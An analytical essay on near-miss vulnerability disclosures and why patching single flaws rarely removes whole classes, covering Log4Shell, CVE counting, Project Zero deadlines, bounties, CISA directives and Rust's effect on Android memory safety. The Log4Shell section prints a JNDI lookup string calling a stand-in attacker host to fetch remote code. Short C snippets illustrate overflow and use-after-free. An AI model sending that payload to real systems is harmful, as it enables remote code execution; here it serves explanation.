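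This could plausibly happen in a security team. Suppose one programmer closes 40 vulnerability reports in a quarter while another spends it converting old queries so that `run` can refuse joined text. At a performance review, the first can show 40 closed reports, but the second can show that some reports never arrived only if the company kept good records of how many used to arrive. But Repenning and Sterman developed the theory from manufacturing and product development, and nobody seems to have tested it on vulnerability reports.

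### A warning about Java, five years early

In December 2021 attackers began exploiting a flaw in Log4j on a huge scale. Log4j is a free library that Java programs use to keep logs, which are records of what a program has done. The flaw, CVE-2021-44228, is usually called Log4Shell. An attack needed little more than a line of text like this:

```
${jndi:ldap://attacker.example/a}
```

It worked in four steps:

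1. The attacker enters the text somewhere a program will record it, such as the username box of a login page.
2. The login fails, and the program passes the username to Log4j for the log.
3. Log4j treats anything inside `${...}` as an instruction to look something up. Here it hands the address to JNDI, a part of Java that fetches objects by name, sometimes from other machines.
4. JNDI contacts the attacker's server, which replies with the location of some Java code. Older versions of Java download the code and run it.

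Researchers had publicly explained the last step five years earlier. *A Journey from JNDI/LDAP Manipulation to Remote Code Execution Dream Land*, a talk by Alvaro Muñoz and Oleksandr Mirosh of Hewlett Packard Enterprise at the Black Hat security conference in August 2016, showed that an outsider who could choose the name in a JNDI lookup could often run code on the server. The technique came from malware that had attacked Java in web browsers in 2015. The class as a whole was therefore no longer a near miss, but for servers the talk was a warning about attacks that might still come.

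Log4j had offered JNDI lookups since 2013, so the flaw already existed at the time of the talk. The talk was not a report about Log4j, and it is unclear whether any of the library's volunteer maintainers heard about it. In 2017 the maintainers added a setting to turn off lookups in log messages, but they left lookups on by default.

Oracle, which develops Java, did make a wider change. In January 2017 it stopped Java from loading remote code by default through two of the protocols that JNDI can use, and in October 2018 it did the same for LDAP, the protocol in the example above. This removed the simplest attack for anyone who updated Java, but organisations kept running old versions. In January 2019, the researcher Michael Stepankin also showed that an attacker could sometimes get the same result with code already on the server.

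Chen Zhaojun of Alibaba's cloud security team reported the Log4j flaw privately on 24 November 2021. It was a near-miss disclosure at that point, since the earliest attack the internet company Cloudflare later found in its records was on 1 December. The flaw became public on 9 December, and mass attacks followed. Log4j's first patch restricted lookups but left another route open. A second version, released within days, removed lookups from log messages and turned JNDI off by default, which the maintainers could have done in 2016.

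The US government's Cyber Safety Review Board judged in its *Review of the December 2021 Log4j Event* (2022) that a focused security review could have found the flaw in 2013, but that the volunteers who maintained Log4j had no resources for one. A single federal department spent 33,000 hours responding to the flaw, but attackers exploited it less than many experts had predicted.

The 2016 Black Hat talk by Muñoz and Mirosh probably did lead to a wider fix in Java itself, though a slow and incomplete one. It could have led to one in Log4j too, because a search for JNDI calls in popular libraries would have turned up the lookup feature. But someone would also have had to realise that ordinary log messages could reach that feature, which is much more obvious now than it was then. Black Hat speakers present dozens of alarming techniques every year, and although Muñoz and Mirosh described a whole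 class of vulnerability, nobody had the job of checking widely used libraries for members of it.

### Most flaws never lead to an attack

Organisations have a reasonable case for doing little. VulnCheck counted 884 exploited flaws in 2025, equal to just under 2% of the roughly 48,000 CVE records published that year, although some of the 884 were older flaws and attackers may yet exploit some of the newer ones. Over a longer period, the share rises to about 6% of all published CVE records, according to *A Visual Exploration of Exploitation in the Wild* (2024) by the Cyentia Institute, a research firm, and FIRST, an association of security response teams. A manager who treats each report as a likely disaster will usually be wrong, and a company that redesigned its product after every report would struggle to ship anything.

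These percentages understate the danger of ignoring reports, since some flaws would have been attacked if their makers had not patched them. That danger is a good reason to patch a reported flaw, but it does not by itself justify fixing the whole vulnerability class.

The better reason is that a whole class carries much more risk than any one of its members. If each flaw has a probability *p* of exploitation, and the flaws are independent, the probability that attackers exploit at least one of *n* flaws is

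1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

If *p* is 2% at the earlier imaginary company, whose programmers add 100 flaws of one class each year, attackers will exploit an average of two flaws from each year's batch, and the chance that they exploit at least one is about 87%. If each exploited flaw costs the company $1 million, the expected loss from a single reported flaw is $20,000, which might justify a day or two of a few programmers' time. The expected loss from a year's batch is $2 million. A $5 million change that kept the whole class out of new code would pay for itself after preventing two and a half years' worth of flaws, but no single report would come close to justifying it.

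A manager who decides case by case can therefore make a sensible decision every time and still leave the company worse off. A process that gives each report its own ticket and small budget is enough for this to happen, even if the manager has no bias about near misses.

The result depends heavily on the inputs. Attackers concentrate on widely used products, so 2% may be far too high for an obscure program and too low for a browser. Attacks also tend to cluster, because an attacker who masters a technique will try it on similar flaws. Clustering leaves the expected number at two but makes a year with no attacks more likely than the formula implies. A company whose customers bear most of the loss will count much less than $1 million as its own loss. For a small class in a little-used product, patching one flaw at a time may well be the right policy.

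### Borrowing from aviation

Some security researchers think the field needs better institutions for learning, and they usually cite aviation as a model. In the United States, pilots and air traffic controllers can send confidential accounts of their own mistakes and close calls to the Aviation Safety Reporting System. NASA, rather than the regulator, runs the system and removes identifying details. The regulator generally waives penalties for unintentional violations if the person reports them within ten days.

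*That Was Close! Reward Reporting of Cybersecurity “Near Misses”* (Bair, Bellovin and colleagues, 2018) proposed a Cyber Safety Reporting System. Organisations would voluntarily report attacks and near misses to a neutral party, possibly in return for some incentive, and researchers and companies could study the combined data. Reporting would be voluntary because a compulsory scheme would be difficult to introduce and might cost more than it was worth. In *Learning from Near Misses*, Adam Shostack, who co-wrote the proposal, blamed mainly the fear of lawsuits for how little the field learns from breaches.

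In 2021, more than 70 experts took part in a four-month workshop at Harvard's Belfer Center that considered the National Transportation Safety Board, which investigates every civil aviation accident in the United States, as a model for computer security. Knake, Shostack and Wheeler (2021), in *Learning from Cyber Incidents*, traced calls for a similar board back to 1991. They doubted that companies would cooperate fully unless the board could compel them to, and recommended keeping fact-finding separate from assigning blame. They also thought near misses might be easier to investigate than successful attacks, because many of the usual obstacles shrink when at least one defence has worked.

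Both proposals mainly concern organisations that come under attack. A near-miss disclosure often involves no attack, and the maker already has the facts. A reporting system could add a comparison across many companies, which might show that the same mistake keeps getting through the same kind of code review. To make this possible, makers would have to report why they made the mistake and what else they checked, as well as which line they changed. CVE records rarely include any of this.

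In 2021, President Biden ordered the creation of a US Cyber Safety Review Board to study significant cyber incidents. It began work in 2022 with members from government and industry. It reviewed the Log4Shell vulnerability, a group of young extortionists called Lapsus$, and a 2023 intrusion into Microsoft's email service. The board had no power to demand evidence, and it covered only serious incidents, so an ordinary near-miss disclosure would not have qualified. In January 2025, the Department of Homeland Security dismissed all the members while they were investigating Salt Typhoon, a Chinese hacking campaign against telephone companies. The board does not appear to have published a review since.

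## How do disclosure rules and bounties favour the single patch?

Most near-miss disclosures go through coordinated vulnerability disclosure, not a review board. Each flaw gets its own identifier, severity score, deadline and sometimes a bounty. A vendor can handle every step well without anyone looking for the same mistake elsewhere.

### One report from start to finish

Suppose the online shop in the earlier example runs on software that a company sells to thousands of retailers. A researcher finds that the search box allows SQL injection. The invoice page has the same flaw, but nobody has noticed. The steps below broadly follow *Establishing a Coordinated Vulnerability Disclosure Program to Work With Security Researchers* (2026), guidance that CISA issued in July with the US National Security Agency and the national cybersecurity bodies of Britain, the Netherlands and Japan.

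1. The report. The researcher sends the maker a short account of the flaw and a proof of concept. The maker tracks how quickly it replies, and CISA suggests two or three business days. CISA's ideal report has a minimal proof of concept, a write-up and an assessment of the impact. To learn about the class at this stage, the maker would also have to ask where else the mistake might occur.

2. Triage. The maker's staff confirm the flaw, rate its severity and check whether anyone has reported it before. CISA makes a similar check when it handles reports itself, according to CISA's *Coordinated Vulnerability Disclosure Process*. A search for duplicates could also reveal that this is the fifth SQL injection flaw of the year, but only if staff label reports by class and somebody counts the labels.

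3. The identifier. An authorised organisation, often the maker itself, assigns a CVE identifier to the search-box flaw. The catalogue now counts one flaw. The invoice page adds to the count only if someone finds that flaw too.

4. The patch. A programmer repairs the query, and the researcher confirms that the trick no longer works. The maker counts the days since the report arrived. To find the invoice page, the programmer would have to search the code for other joined queries before moving on to the next report.

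5. The advisory. The maker tells customers which versions are vulnerable, how serious the flaw is and what to install. It should also name the root cause, for example with the label CWE-89. The organisation that assigned the identifier has 72 hours after disclosure to publish a CVE record. A rival who reads the label could check its own products for SQL injection, but nobody follows up to see whether it does.

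6. Closure. The maker closes the report and records whether it met the deadline. Any work on the class now needs a new task, such as converting the remaining queries, with its own owner and budget. No researcher is waiting for that task, and no publication date hangs over it.

### How the CVE catalogue counts flaws

The CVE Program tells the organisations that assign identifiers to consider whether flaws are "independently fixable", meaning that a programmer could repair one without repairing the other. Flaws that pass this test should get separate identifiers, so the flaws in the search box and the invoice page would get one each. If the organisation is unsure, it should assign only one identifier.

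The programme previously used vulnerability type to decide how many identifiers to assign. *CVE Counting* (2016), a CVE Program draft, proposed using independent fixability instead. Under the earlier rule, the two SQL injection flaws could have shared an identifier.

When many programs use a feature insecurely, the current rules also give each vulnerable program its own identifier if the feature can be used securely, and assign a single identifier to the whole problem if it can't. Databases accept parameterised queries, so each program that is vulnerable because it builds queries by joining strings gets its own identifier, and the database that accepts those queries gets none. This makes sense for customers, who need to know which program to update, but it leaves the catalogue with thousands of records of programmers' mistakes and no record of the interface that makes the mistake so easy.

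There are exceptions, such as insecure default settings, which organisations should usually treat as vulnerabilities, so researchers can report a design choice. Another is CVE-2004-2761, which concerns a cryptographic algorithm that became insecure as computers improved. Any product using the algorithm might share this weakness.

Counting flaws separately matters because governments and companies attach deadlines, scores and payments to each flaw. Any catalogue needs a unit, and this one does not stop anyone from fixing a whole class.

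### Deadlines speed up patches

Disclosure seems to prompt software makers to release patches sooner. Arora, Krishnan, Telang and Yang (2010), in *An Empirical Analysis of Software Vendors' Patch Release Behavior*, estimated that disclosing a flaw multiplied the maker's chance of releasing a patch at any given moment by nearly two and a half. For example, if a maker had a 1% chance of releasing a patch on any given day, its median time to a patch would be about 69 days. Raising that chance to 2.5% would cut the median to about 27 days. The data come from the early 2000s, so the size of the effect may be different today.

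Project Zero's experience also suggests that disclosure deadlines speed up fixes. When the team began in 2014, some makers took more than six months to fix a flaw. Project Zero told makers it would publish the details after 90 days, and by 2019 they were fixing 97.7% of the flaws it reported within the deadline, according to Willis (2020). There was no comparison group, and makers may also have become faster for other reasons.

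A fast patch can still be incomplete, though. FreeType's 2014 patch put a check in the wrong place, but a measure of patch speed would count it the same as a patch that closed both routes. Neither Arora and colleagues' estimate nor Project Zero's 97.7% measures how many related flaws the makers left behind.

Abolishing deadlines would probably not help. Makers who took six months in 2014 had twice as long as Project Zero now gives, and nobody has shown that they used the time to look for variants or change their interfaces.

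### Project Zero's attempt to get deeper patches

By 2020, Project Zero was worried about shallow patches. Willis wrote that vendors had too often been "papering over the cracks" and admitted that the team's emphasis on speed might be making this worse. Project Zero therefore added thorough patching to its goals and changed its policy for a one-year trial.

Project Zero's old policy allowed it to publish the details of a flaw as soon as the maker fixed it, but under the new one it waited the full 90 days unless both sides agreed otherwise. Willis expected makers to use the whole period to find the root cause and look for variants. If a patch proved incomplete, Project Zero would add the details to the original report, which might already be public, and would not start a new deadline, so the maker couldn't count on another 90 days of secrecy.

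But the trial also rewarded speed, as Willis intended. The table shows how many days users had to install a patch before Project Zero published the details.

| Policy | Patch on day 20 | Patch on day 80 |
|---|---|---|
| 2019 | As few as 0 | As few as 0 |
| 2020 trial | 70 | 10 |
| 2021 onwards | 30 | 30 |

In the trial, a maker who spent an extra 60 days looking for variants left its users 60 fewer days to install the patch before disclosure. A maker worried about slow updates therefore had good reason to ship a patch for only the reported flaw.

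Willis (2021) reported that the trial had not significantly changed how long makers took to develop patches, and gave no results on thoroughness. Project Zero then focused on speed again. It kept the 90-day deadline, but if the maker met it, the team would publish the details 30 days after the patch. Thorough patching remained a goal, and variants of flaws that Project Zero had already reported still got no new deadline.

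The 2021 policy may leave more room for careful work than the trial did, because a maker can use most of the 90 days without shortening the time its users have to update. It is unknown whether makers do this. Willis hoped to cut the periods to 84 and 28 days for 2022, but Project Zero was still using 90 and 30 days when Willis (2025) announced another trial.

Soon after the 2020 trial, Stone renewed the call for thorough investigation and patching, based on that year's zero-days. Those zero-days can't show whether the trial worked, because several of the original flaws predated it.

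Project Zero was asking for something narrower than a class-level fix. The shop software's maker could probably find its other joined queries within 90 days, but converting them all and then forbidding the unsafe interface might take years in a large product. The root cause Project Zero asks for is often a missing check in one program, which the maker can correct without changing the language that let a programmer omit it.

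The deadline is much shorter once attackers are using a flaw, at seven days under Google Project Zero's *90+30 policy*. A near miss therefore gives the maker far more time for careful work than an attack does, if the maker chooses to use it.

### What secrecy costs

Until the maker publishes the flaw, only a few people know about it. This protects users, but other makers can't check their own products for the same mistake. CISA warns that a secret is more likely to leak when many organisations share it, which is a good reason to keep the group small.

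Widening the group also creates a timing problem. Lin, Hassan and Adams found that when a flaw affected products from several organisations, the median gap between the first patch and the last was 35 days, and some gaps lasted more than a year. During that time, attackers can study the first patch and attack the products that don't have one yet.

Project Zero has had to weigh the same drawbacks. Willis acknowledged in 2021 that waiting 30 days after a patch would make it harder for defenders to find variants quickly. In the 2025 trial, Project Zero began announcing within about a week that it had reported a flaw. It named the maker, the product and the dates but not the kind of flaw, so another maker would not know what to look for.

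Delaying disclosure by a few months probably matters little when a vulnerability class has lasted for decades. Permanent secrecy is worse because other companies may never learn about the mistake. Some makers repair a flaw without mentioning it or require researchers to sign non-disclosure agreements, and CISA advises against both practices.

### Severity scores and federal deadlines

Makers and their customers often rank flaws with the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), which scores the severity of each flaw from 0 to 10 but doesn't score a class as a whole. If the shop software has twenty moderately serious flaws with the same cause, they may address a single critical flaw before any of the twenty, even if the twenty together are more dangerous.

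In June 2026 the US government changed how civilian federal agencies decide what to patch first. The new order, Binding Operational Directive 26-04, replaces a stricter focus on the KEV catalogue with four factors, which CISA (2026) listed in its announcement:

- whether the vulnerable machine is publicly exposed
- whether the flaw is in the KEV catalogue
- whether an attacker could automate the whole attack
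- how much control the attacker would gain

If a flaw is at the dangerous end on all four factors, the agency has three days to fix it and must check whether an intruder has already got in, according to the law firm Wiley Rein's *CISA Directive Highlights Risk-Based Vulnerability Management* (2026). The firm called the timelines "aggressive, bordering on unrealistic". SecurityWeek's *CISA Directs Federal Agencies to Prioritize Security Patches Based on Risk* reports that some other combinations also carry the three-day deadline, and that less urgent flaws get 14 or 60 days. Inside Privacy's *CISA Releases Binding Operational Directive on Prioritizing Security Updates Based on Risk* describes a further category that can wait until the machine's next major upgrade.

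Agencies must start following these deadlines by 7 December 2026. FedRAMP (2026), the programme that certifies cloud services for government use, will require cloud providers to follow similar rules from the same date.

An agency would assess the twentieth SQL injection flaw in a product just as it assessed the first. *BOD 26-04* (2026) explains that CISA publishes three of the four answers in this assessment for every CVE identifier. This saves agencies work, but it also makes the individual CVE record even more central to their routine.

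The directive binds the agencies that install patches, and they can't rewrite a supplier's product, so it would be unfair to blame the directive for not fixing whole vulnerability classes. An agency with a three-day deadline needs a working patch from its supplier. It could consider a supplier's long history of similar flaws when it next buys software, but that is a separate decision.

Kevin Greene of the security company BeyondTrust told SecurityWeek that the directive was "narrowly focused on CVE prioritization". Greene wanted agencies to remove unnecessary privileges as well, so that an intruder who exploited one flaw could do less damage. BeyondTrust sells software for managing privileges, but the argument is sound, because removing privileges also limits the harm from flaws that nobody has reported yet. FedRAMP leaves some room for this approach. A cloud provider need not remove a flaw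 completely if it mitigates the flaw enough that attackers can no longer automate the attack or reach the flaw from the internet.

### Bounties

A bug bounty is a payment to someone who reports a flaw. Say the shop software's maker pays $2,000 for each page with an SQL injection flaw, and the researcher suspects that twenty pages contain the same mistake. The researcher could earn $40,000 by reporting them separately. Explaining the pattern in the first report might cost the researcher most of that money, because the maker could then find the other pages itself.

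Some makers instead pay one bounty for all the flaws that share a cause. The researcher then earns the same $2,000 for reporting the flaw on one page or on twenty, and has no financial reason to look at the other nineteen. Under both arrangements, the maker pays nothing extra for advice on how to prevent the mistake.

Researchers also compete with each other, because bounty programmes commonly pay only the first person to report a flaw. A researcher who spends two weeks tracing the cause may lose the whole payment to someone who sent a proof of concept after an hour.

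Unpaid duplicate reports can be informative. If six people independently report the same flaw within a month, it is probably easy to find, and the review that missed it may have missed others like it. Staff who close five of those reports as duplicates will lose that warning unless somebody counts them.

The maker's incentives are mixed. It saves $2,000 on each variant its own programmers find, which gives it a reason to search. But converting every query in a large product may cost much more than $40,000 in bounties, so the bounties alone may not persuade a manager to fix the class.

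Money may shape researchers' behaviour less than this argument from incentives implies. Many enjoy explaining a root cause, or want the reputation that a good explanation brings. Companies can also pay for broader work, as Microsoft did in 2012 when it awarded $200,000 through its BlueHat Prize for a defence against a common way of exploiting memory safety flaws. The winning idea was only a mitigation, but its inventor did not have to report any flaws to win.

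### How individual reports make classes visible

The main purpose of disclosure is to protect current users from a known flaw, rather than to prevent similar flaws. A retailer with a vulnerable search box needs a patch this week, whether or not the software's maker later redesigns its database code. Holding back the patch until the whole class of flaws was gone would leave every customer exposed.

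Disclosure records are also the main source for studying vulnerability classes. MITRE's yearly ranking of weaknesses and CISA's calculation of the 41.5% share for stubborn weaknesses both depend on thousands of records of individual flaws. Giving each independently fixable flaw its own record even helps analysts see patterns. If a maker fixes twenty SQL injection flaws, twenty records can show a pattern that one combined record might hide.

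That depends on good labels. The CVE Program requires each record to give the type or cause of the flaw. It recommends using CWE for this but doesn't require it, and an organisation that can't yet determine the cause may say so. In its July guidance, CISA asks makers to choose labels that convey the root cause. Starks reported that CISA also outlined a plan to improve the CVE Program in 2026. MITRE has complained that existing labels are often too general, so better ones would especially help people who study vulnerability classes.

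Even an accurate label describes the flaw, not how the maker fixed it. Two companies could both publish a record marked CWE-89 (SQL injection), one after changing a single line and the other after banning queries built by joining strings throughout its code. The CVE Program encourages organisations to explain how flaws and fixes are related where this is useful, but does not require them to record whether anyone searched for variants. An incomplete patch may get a new identifier or share the old one, so the catalogue isn't a reliable measure of how often patches fail.

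Someone also has to look at flaws across companies. The White House's Gold Eagle clearinghouse might be well placed to do that. Inside Privacy's *White House Launches Gold Eagle AI Cybersecurity Clearinghouse* describes it as taking in flaws from many industries.

### What the July 2026 guidance asks makers to do

CISA and its partners do ask makers to look beyond the reported flaw. They say development teams should search for other flaws of the same class, especially the "unforgivable" ones that Christey described in 2007. They also ask makers to formally report classes that keep recurring in their products to senior leaders, using figures and trends to show why the company needs a plan to eliminate them.

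By itself, the search for other examples leads only to more fixes for individual flaws. The message to senior leaders could lead to a fix for the whole class, because it shows them a year's worth of similar flaws together and they can give a programmer six months to replace an interface.

But the guidance is voluntary, and these recommendations take up only a few sentences of a 12-page document. CISA suggests no deadline for the search or the plan, and does not ask makers to publish the results. It tells makers only to consider bounties, and does not suggest paying more for a report that identifies a pattern. The guidance is less than five months old, so it is too early to expect evidence of whether companies follow it.

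Makers who do follow it may look worse for a while. CISA wants them to assign CVE identifiers to flaws of these kinds whether their own staff or outsiders find them. If the shop software's maker searches its code and finds nineteen more vulnerable pages, it should publish nineteen more records. A competitor that never searched would have a shorter list, and a customer comparing lists could easily choose the less secure product.

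## Why did memory safety take decades, and what finally reduced the flaws?

Memory safety is the longest-running test of whether patching flaws one at a time works. Microsoft's *We need a safer systems programming language* (2019) reported that memory safety flaws had made up a nearly constant share of its CVEs for over a decade, despite better tools and guidance. In Android, their share fell from 76% in 2019 to below 20% in 2025, mainly because Google switched to memory-safe languages for new code. Languages that prevent most of these flaws existed before the first major attack that exploited such a flaw, so the delay wasn't caused by not knowing how to prevent them.

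### Two ways to misuse memory

Programmers have written most operating systems, browsers and device software in C or its descendant C++. Both languages let a program read or write at almost any memory address it can calculate, and generally leave it to the programmer to check that the address is sensible, which keeps programs small and fast.

In a buffer overflow, a program writes past the end of the memory it reserved:

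```
char name[8];                // room for eight characters
int  is_admin = 0;           // 0 means no
strcpy(name, typed_text);    // copies until the text ends
```

If the compiler places `is_admin` directly after `name` and a customer types nine letters, the ninth lands in `is_admin`. Any value except 0 means yes, so the customer becomes an administrator. Attackers have more often aimed at the return address, which sits in the same area of memory and records where the processor should continue when a function ends. They can choose what runs next by overwriting it.

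In a use-after-free, a program gives memory back and then carries on using it:

```
order = malloc(64);             // reserve 64 bytes for Ana's order
free(order);                    // Ana cancels, so the bytes are available
note = malloc(64);              // the program may get the same bytes back
copy_text(note, typed_text);    // Ana's message goes into them
charge(order->price);           // part of the message becomes the price
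```

Ana can now set the price. Real records often also contain the address of a function, which can let an attacker choose what code the program runs.

### Fifty years of warnings

In a 1972 planning study for the US Air Force, the consultant James Anderson described how a program that failed to check where it was copying data could let a user overwrite part of the operating system. In November 1988, a graduate student named Robert Morris released a worm, a program that copies itself from machine to machine. It spread partly by sending 536 characters to a service that had reserved room for 512. *The Urgent Need for Memory Safety in Software Products*, which Lord wrote for CISA, attributes the major internet outage that followed to memory-unsafe code.

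The service read its input with a C function called `gets`, which cannot check whether the input fits in the memory set aside for it. Administrators patched the service, but the committee that published the first C standard a year later kept `gets` and removed it only in 2011. So even a famous attack led to fixes for individual instances, while the function that made the mistake easy remained in C for another 23 years.

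In 2024 Google sorted the industry's responses to memory safety flaws into four generations: patching, mitigation, searching for flaws, and prevention. The generations overlap in time but follow a rough order.

Patching was the first response, and the worms of 2001 showed its limits. Code Red, which infected more than 350,000 machines in a day that July, used a buffer overflow in Microsoft's web server. The security company eEye had reported the flaw, and Microsoft had issued a patch a month earlier. This near-miss disclosure had been handled properly, but the worm spread through machines whose owners hadn't installed the patch. Nimda followed in September, spreading partly through flaws unrelated to memory.

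In a January 2002 memo, Bill Gates told Microsoft's employees to put security ahead of new features. The company then stopped most work on Windows for about two months to train its programmers and review their code. It took attacks to bring about this change, and Microsoft still went on writing Windows in C and C++. A year after the memo, another worm, Slammer, spread through a buffer overflow in Microsoft's database software. Microsoft had released a patch for it six months earlier.

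### Mitigations and searching

Around the same time, makers began to adopt mitigations that interfere with the usual ways of exploiting a memory flaw. Two of the best known are:

- Stack canaries. The compiler puts a secret random value between a function's variables and its return address, and the program checks the value before the function ends. An overflow that reaches the return address normally changes the canary on the way, so the program stops.
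- Address randomisation. The operating system loads parts of a program at unpredictable places, so an attacker who can redirect the program doesn't know where to send it.

Both defences leave the mistake in the code. In the example above, the overflow changes `is_admin` without reaching a canary, unless the compiler has rearranged the variables. A second flaw that lets an attacker read memory can reveal the canary or the program's location. Safronov, Allott and Bostan (2024), in *How Memory-Safe is IoT?*, note that canaries and similar measures target overflows and do little to stop the use of freed memory, a flaw they often found in routers. Google's main objection is that mitigations can slow products down and force trade-offs between security and other requirements.

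Makers also searched for flaws before attackers could find them. A fuzzer is a tool that feeds a program enormous numbers of odd inputs, and a sanitizer makes the program stop with an error report as soon as it misuses memory. Google, which built many of these tools, found that teams needed constant pressure to run the fuzzers, sort the results and fix the flaws, and that heavily fuzzed code still contained flaws. Fuzzing also doesn't stop programmers from adding new ones.

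Microsoft's flat proportion fits that account but doesn't prove it, because the proportion would also have stayed flat if all kinds of flaw had become rarer at the same rate.

### Preventing the flaws in the language

To prevent both examples, a language has to keep every access within bounds and ensure that a program never uses memory after giving it back. The first is fairly simple. The language stores each array's length with the array and checks each access against it.

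For the second, languages such as Java use a garbage collector. It periodically finds and reclaims memory that the program can no longer reach, so the programmer never calls `free`. As long as `order` still points to Ana's order, the collector does not reclaim those 64 bytes. Lisp had a garbage collector by about 1960, long before the Morris worm.

But a garbage collector uses processor time and extra memory, at moments the programmer doesn't fully control. Many programs can tolerate this, but it is awkward in the core of an operating system or in a phone's modem, where a memory flaw does the most damage. Lord argues that until a few years ago programmers had no language that combined the speed of C with built-in memory safety. That is probably the best single explanation for the delay, although it doesn't excuse everything, since dropping `gets` in 1989 would barely have slowed programs.

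Rust, which a Mozilla engineer began in 2006 and which reached version 1.0 in 2015, does most of the work before the program runs. As Red Hat Research Quarterly explains, each region of memory has exactly one owner, and the compiler adds the code that frees the region once the owner is finished with it. Other parts of the program can borrow the memory, but only while the owner still exists:

```
let order = String::from("pens");
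let label = &order;        // label borrows the order
drop(order);               // the compiler refuses: label still needs it
println!("{}", label);
```

A C compiler would normally accept the equivalent program, but the Rust compiler rejects it, so the flaw never reaches a customer. Rust also allows data to have either one borrower that can change it or any number that can only read it at a time. This prevents one part of a program from lengthening a list, which can move it to a new place in memory, while another part is still reading from the old place.

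Rust checks array bounds mostly while the program runs, and stops the program if a check fails. So an attacker may still be able to crash a Rust program with a bad length, but not overwrite its memory.

### What unsafe code leaves open

Some necessary operations break these rules. A program that controls hardware has to write to particular addresses, and a program that calls a C library has to trust pointers the compiler can't check. Rust lets programmers do this inside a block marked `unsafe`, where they do part of the checking themselves. They normally wrap the block in a safe interface so that other programmers can use it without taking the same risk.

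A mistake in the unsafe block breaks the guarantee for everyone who relies on it. *An In-Depth Study with All Rust CVEs* (2020) found that every memory safety bug it examined needed unsafe code, except one caused by the compiler. A tool called Rudra later checked 43,000 Rust packages and, according to Georgia Tech, found 264 previously unknown memory safety bugs, including two in Rust's standard library.

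Bae (2026), in *Memory Safety Bugs in Rust Standard Library*, reported that a Microsoft team with an AI scanner had since found several more flaws there, including some that a program written entirely in safe Rust could trigger. Bae traced them to mistaken assumptions that code would not fail halfway through, and that functions supplied by the library's users and the underlying system would behave correctly. For example, unsafe code might reserve memory for the number of items a user's function tells it to expect, then overflow that memory when more arrive. Cook and colleagues are coordinating an effort to prove that the library has no such flaws, but it contains about 34,000 functions and a new version appears every six weeks.

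Bugs are also hard to catch where Rust calls code in other languages. *A Study of Undefined Behavior Across Foreign Function Boundaries in Rust Libraries* (McCormack, Sunshine and Aldrich, 2024) pointed out that Miri, the only tool that could check a running program against Rust's rules for sharing memory, could not find bugs in the C functions that a Rust program calls. The Rust compiler can also have bugs. *Claude Found a Seven-Year Bug in the Rust Compiler* (Faisal, 2026) described a five-line program in safe Rust that reads freed memory, one of the results of Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026).

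Lists like this can make Rust look worse than it is. In *How memory safety CVEs differ between Rust and C/C++*, Kobzol (2026) warned against comparing the languages by their CVE records, because Rust and C/C++ programmers treat potential flaws in libraries differently. Rust programmers usually regard a library as vulnerable if any safe program could corrupt memory through it, even if no such program exists. If the library were written in C, the calling program would often be blamed instead. Rust still doesn't make memory safety flaws impossible, only very rare, and data is needed to determine how rare.

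### What happened in Android

The best data come from Android, whose team began to favour memory-safe languages for new code around 2019. Google attributes the change to the rising cost and complexity of dealing with memory safety flaws. So the accumulated expense of many individual reports prompted the change, rather than any single disclosure.

Google left most of the old C and C++ in place and kept writing C++. *Rust in Android* (Vander Stoep, 2025) reports that by 2025 Google's own programmers were adding slightly more Rust than C++, after subtracting deleted code. The proportion of flaws that involved memory safety still fell.

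The absolute number of memory safety flaws also fell, so their falling proportion was not simply the result of other flaws multiplying. The Hacker News (2025) gives 223 memory safety flaws for 2019. Google estimated 36 for 2024, based on a count of 27 by September. These numbers and the published percentages together give a rough figure for all other flaws.

| | 2019 | 2024 |
|---|---|---|
| Memory safety flaws | 223 | 36 |
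| Share of all Android flaws | 76% | 24% |
| Other flaws (calculated) | about 70 | about 114 |

Memory safety flaws fell by 84% in five years, while other flaws rose by around 60%. That rise is about what you would expect in a growing program. In Google's simulation, which used numbers similar to Android's, the code doubled every six years. If flaws grew at the same rate, 70 would become 125 in five years.

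Google can't attribute the whole fall in Android's memory safety flaws to new languages. The flaws declined faster than its simulation predicted, and Google suggested that parallel work on the old code might be the reason. There is also no comparable version of Android that stayed with C++. But patching, mitigations and fuzzing had all been in use for years without producing such a fall, and the change of language is the obvious new factor.

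Google does not seem to have published a proportion for 2026, but memory flaws haven't disappeared. RodHat's *Android 17 QPR2* (2026) described 85 fixes in December, including fixes for a write outside memory bounds in a video decoder and a timing error that corrupts memory in the code for carriers' voice services. Google knew of no attacks on any of the 85 flaws. *Android's November 2026 Updates Patch Over 200 Vulnerabilities* (Arghire, 2026) reported a much larger batch the month before. These totals can't be compared with the yearly figures, because Android's monthly bulletins usually include flaws in chip makers' components, and a large batch may only mean that people are searching harder.

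### One flaw in five million lines

Vander Stoep also estimated the number of memory safety flaws per million lines of code in each language. Android's Rust code, about 5 million lines, had one known memory safety flaw, or 0.2 per million. Google's historical figure for C and C++ is closer to 1,000 per million.

The Rust figure rests on a single flaw in 5 million lines. If flaws turn up at random, that is compatible with a true rate from about 0.005 to 1.1 per million lines. Even the top of that range is about 900 times lower than the C and C++ figure.

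The age of the code is a bigger worry. Google has had decades to find flaws in C and C++, but most of Android's Rust is only a few years old. If flaws take 2.5 years to find on average and the typical line of Rust is two years old, people have found only about 55% of the flaws in it. They may also have looked less hard in Rust because they expected to find less. But even if AI scanners found another 20 flaws in the same 5 million lines, the density would rise to 4.2 per million, still about 240 times lower than in C and C++. The exact ratio is unreliable, but only a very large error would eliminate the difference.

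The same figures are evidence against the fear that unsafe Rust is as bad as C. About 4% of Android's Rust, or roughly 200,000 lines, is in unsafe blocks. At the historical density for C and C++, those lines would contain 200 memory safety flaws, but Google knew of only one.

### The near miss in CrabbyAVIF

That one flaw is CVE-2025-48530, the near miss in the CrabbyAVIF image library, a buffer overflow in unsafe Rust code. No public release contained it, but Google assigned a CVE identifier so that the patch would get priority and staff could track it.

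Even if the flaw had shipped, Android's default memory allocator, Scudo, would have protected many users. It places guard pages, which are stretches of memory that no program may touch, around the large blocks of memory it gives to programs. The overflow ran into a guard page, which crashed the program before the overflow could damage anything. The crash helped Google identify the flaw, but the crash report didn't make clear that an overflow was the cause, which slowed the response.

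Afterwards, Google changed the crash reports to clearly identify an overflow into a guard page and began writing a section on unsafe code for its Rust course. Scudo is the default but not required, so Google kept working with phone makers to make it required. Google said that in the meantime it would issue CVE identifiers for sufficiently severe flaws even where Scudo could stop them.

Google's changes went beyond fixing the one bug, and they show a company learning from a flaw that hurt nobody. They don't make the mistake impossible, though. Vander Stoep considers a ban on unsafe code unworkable in an operating system, so Google settled for better detection, better training and wider use of a mitigation. It could accept this because the decision to use Rust had already confined the problem to a small part of the code.

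### The price of rewriting

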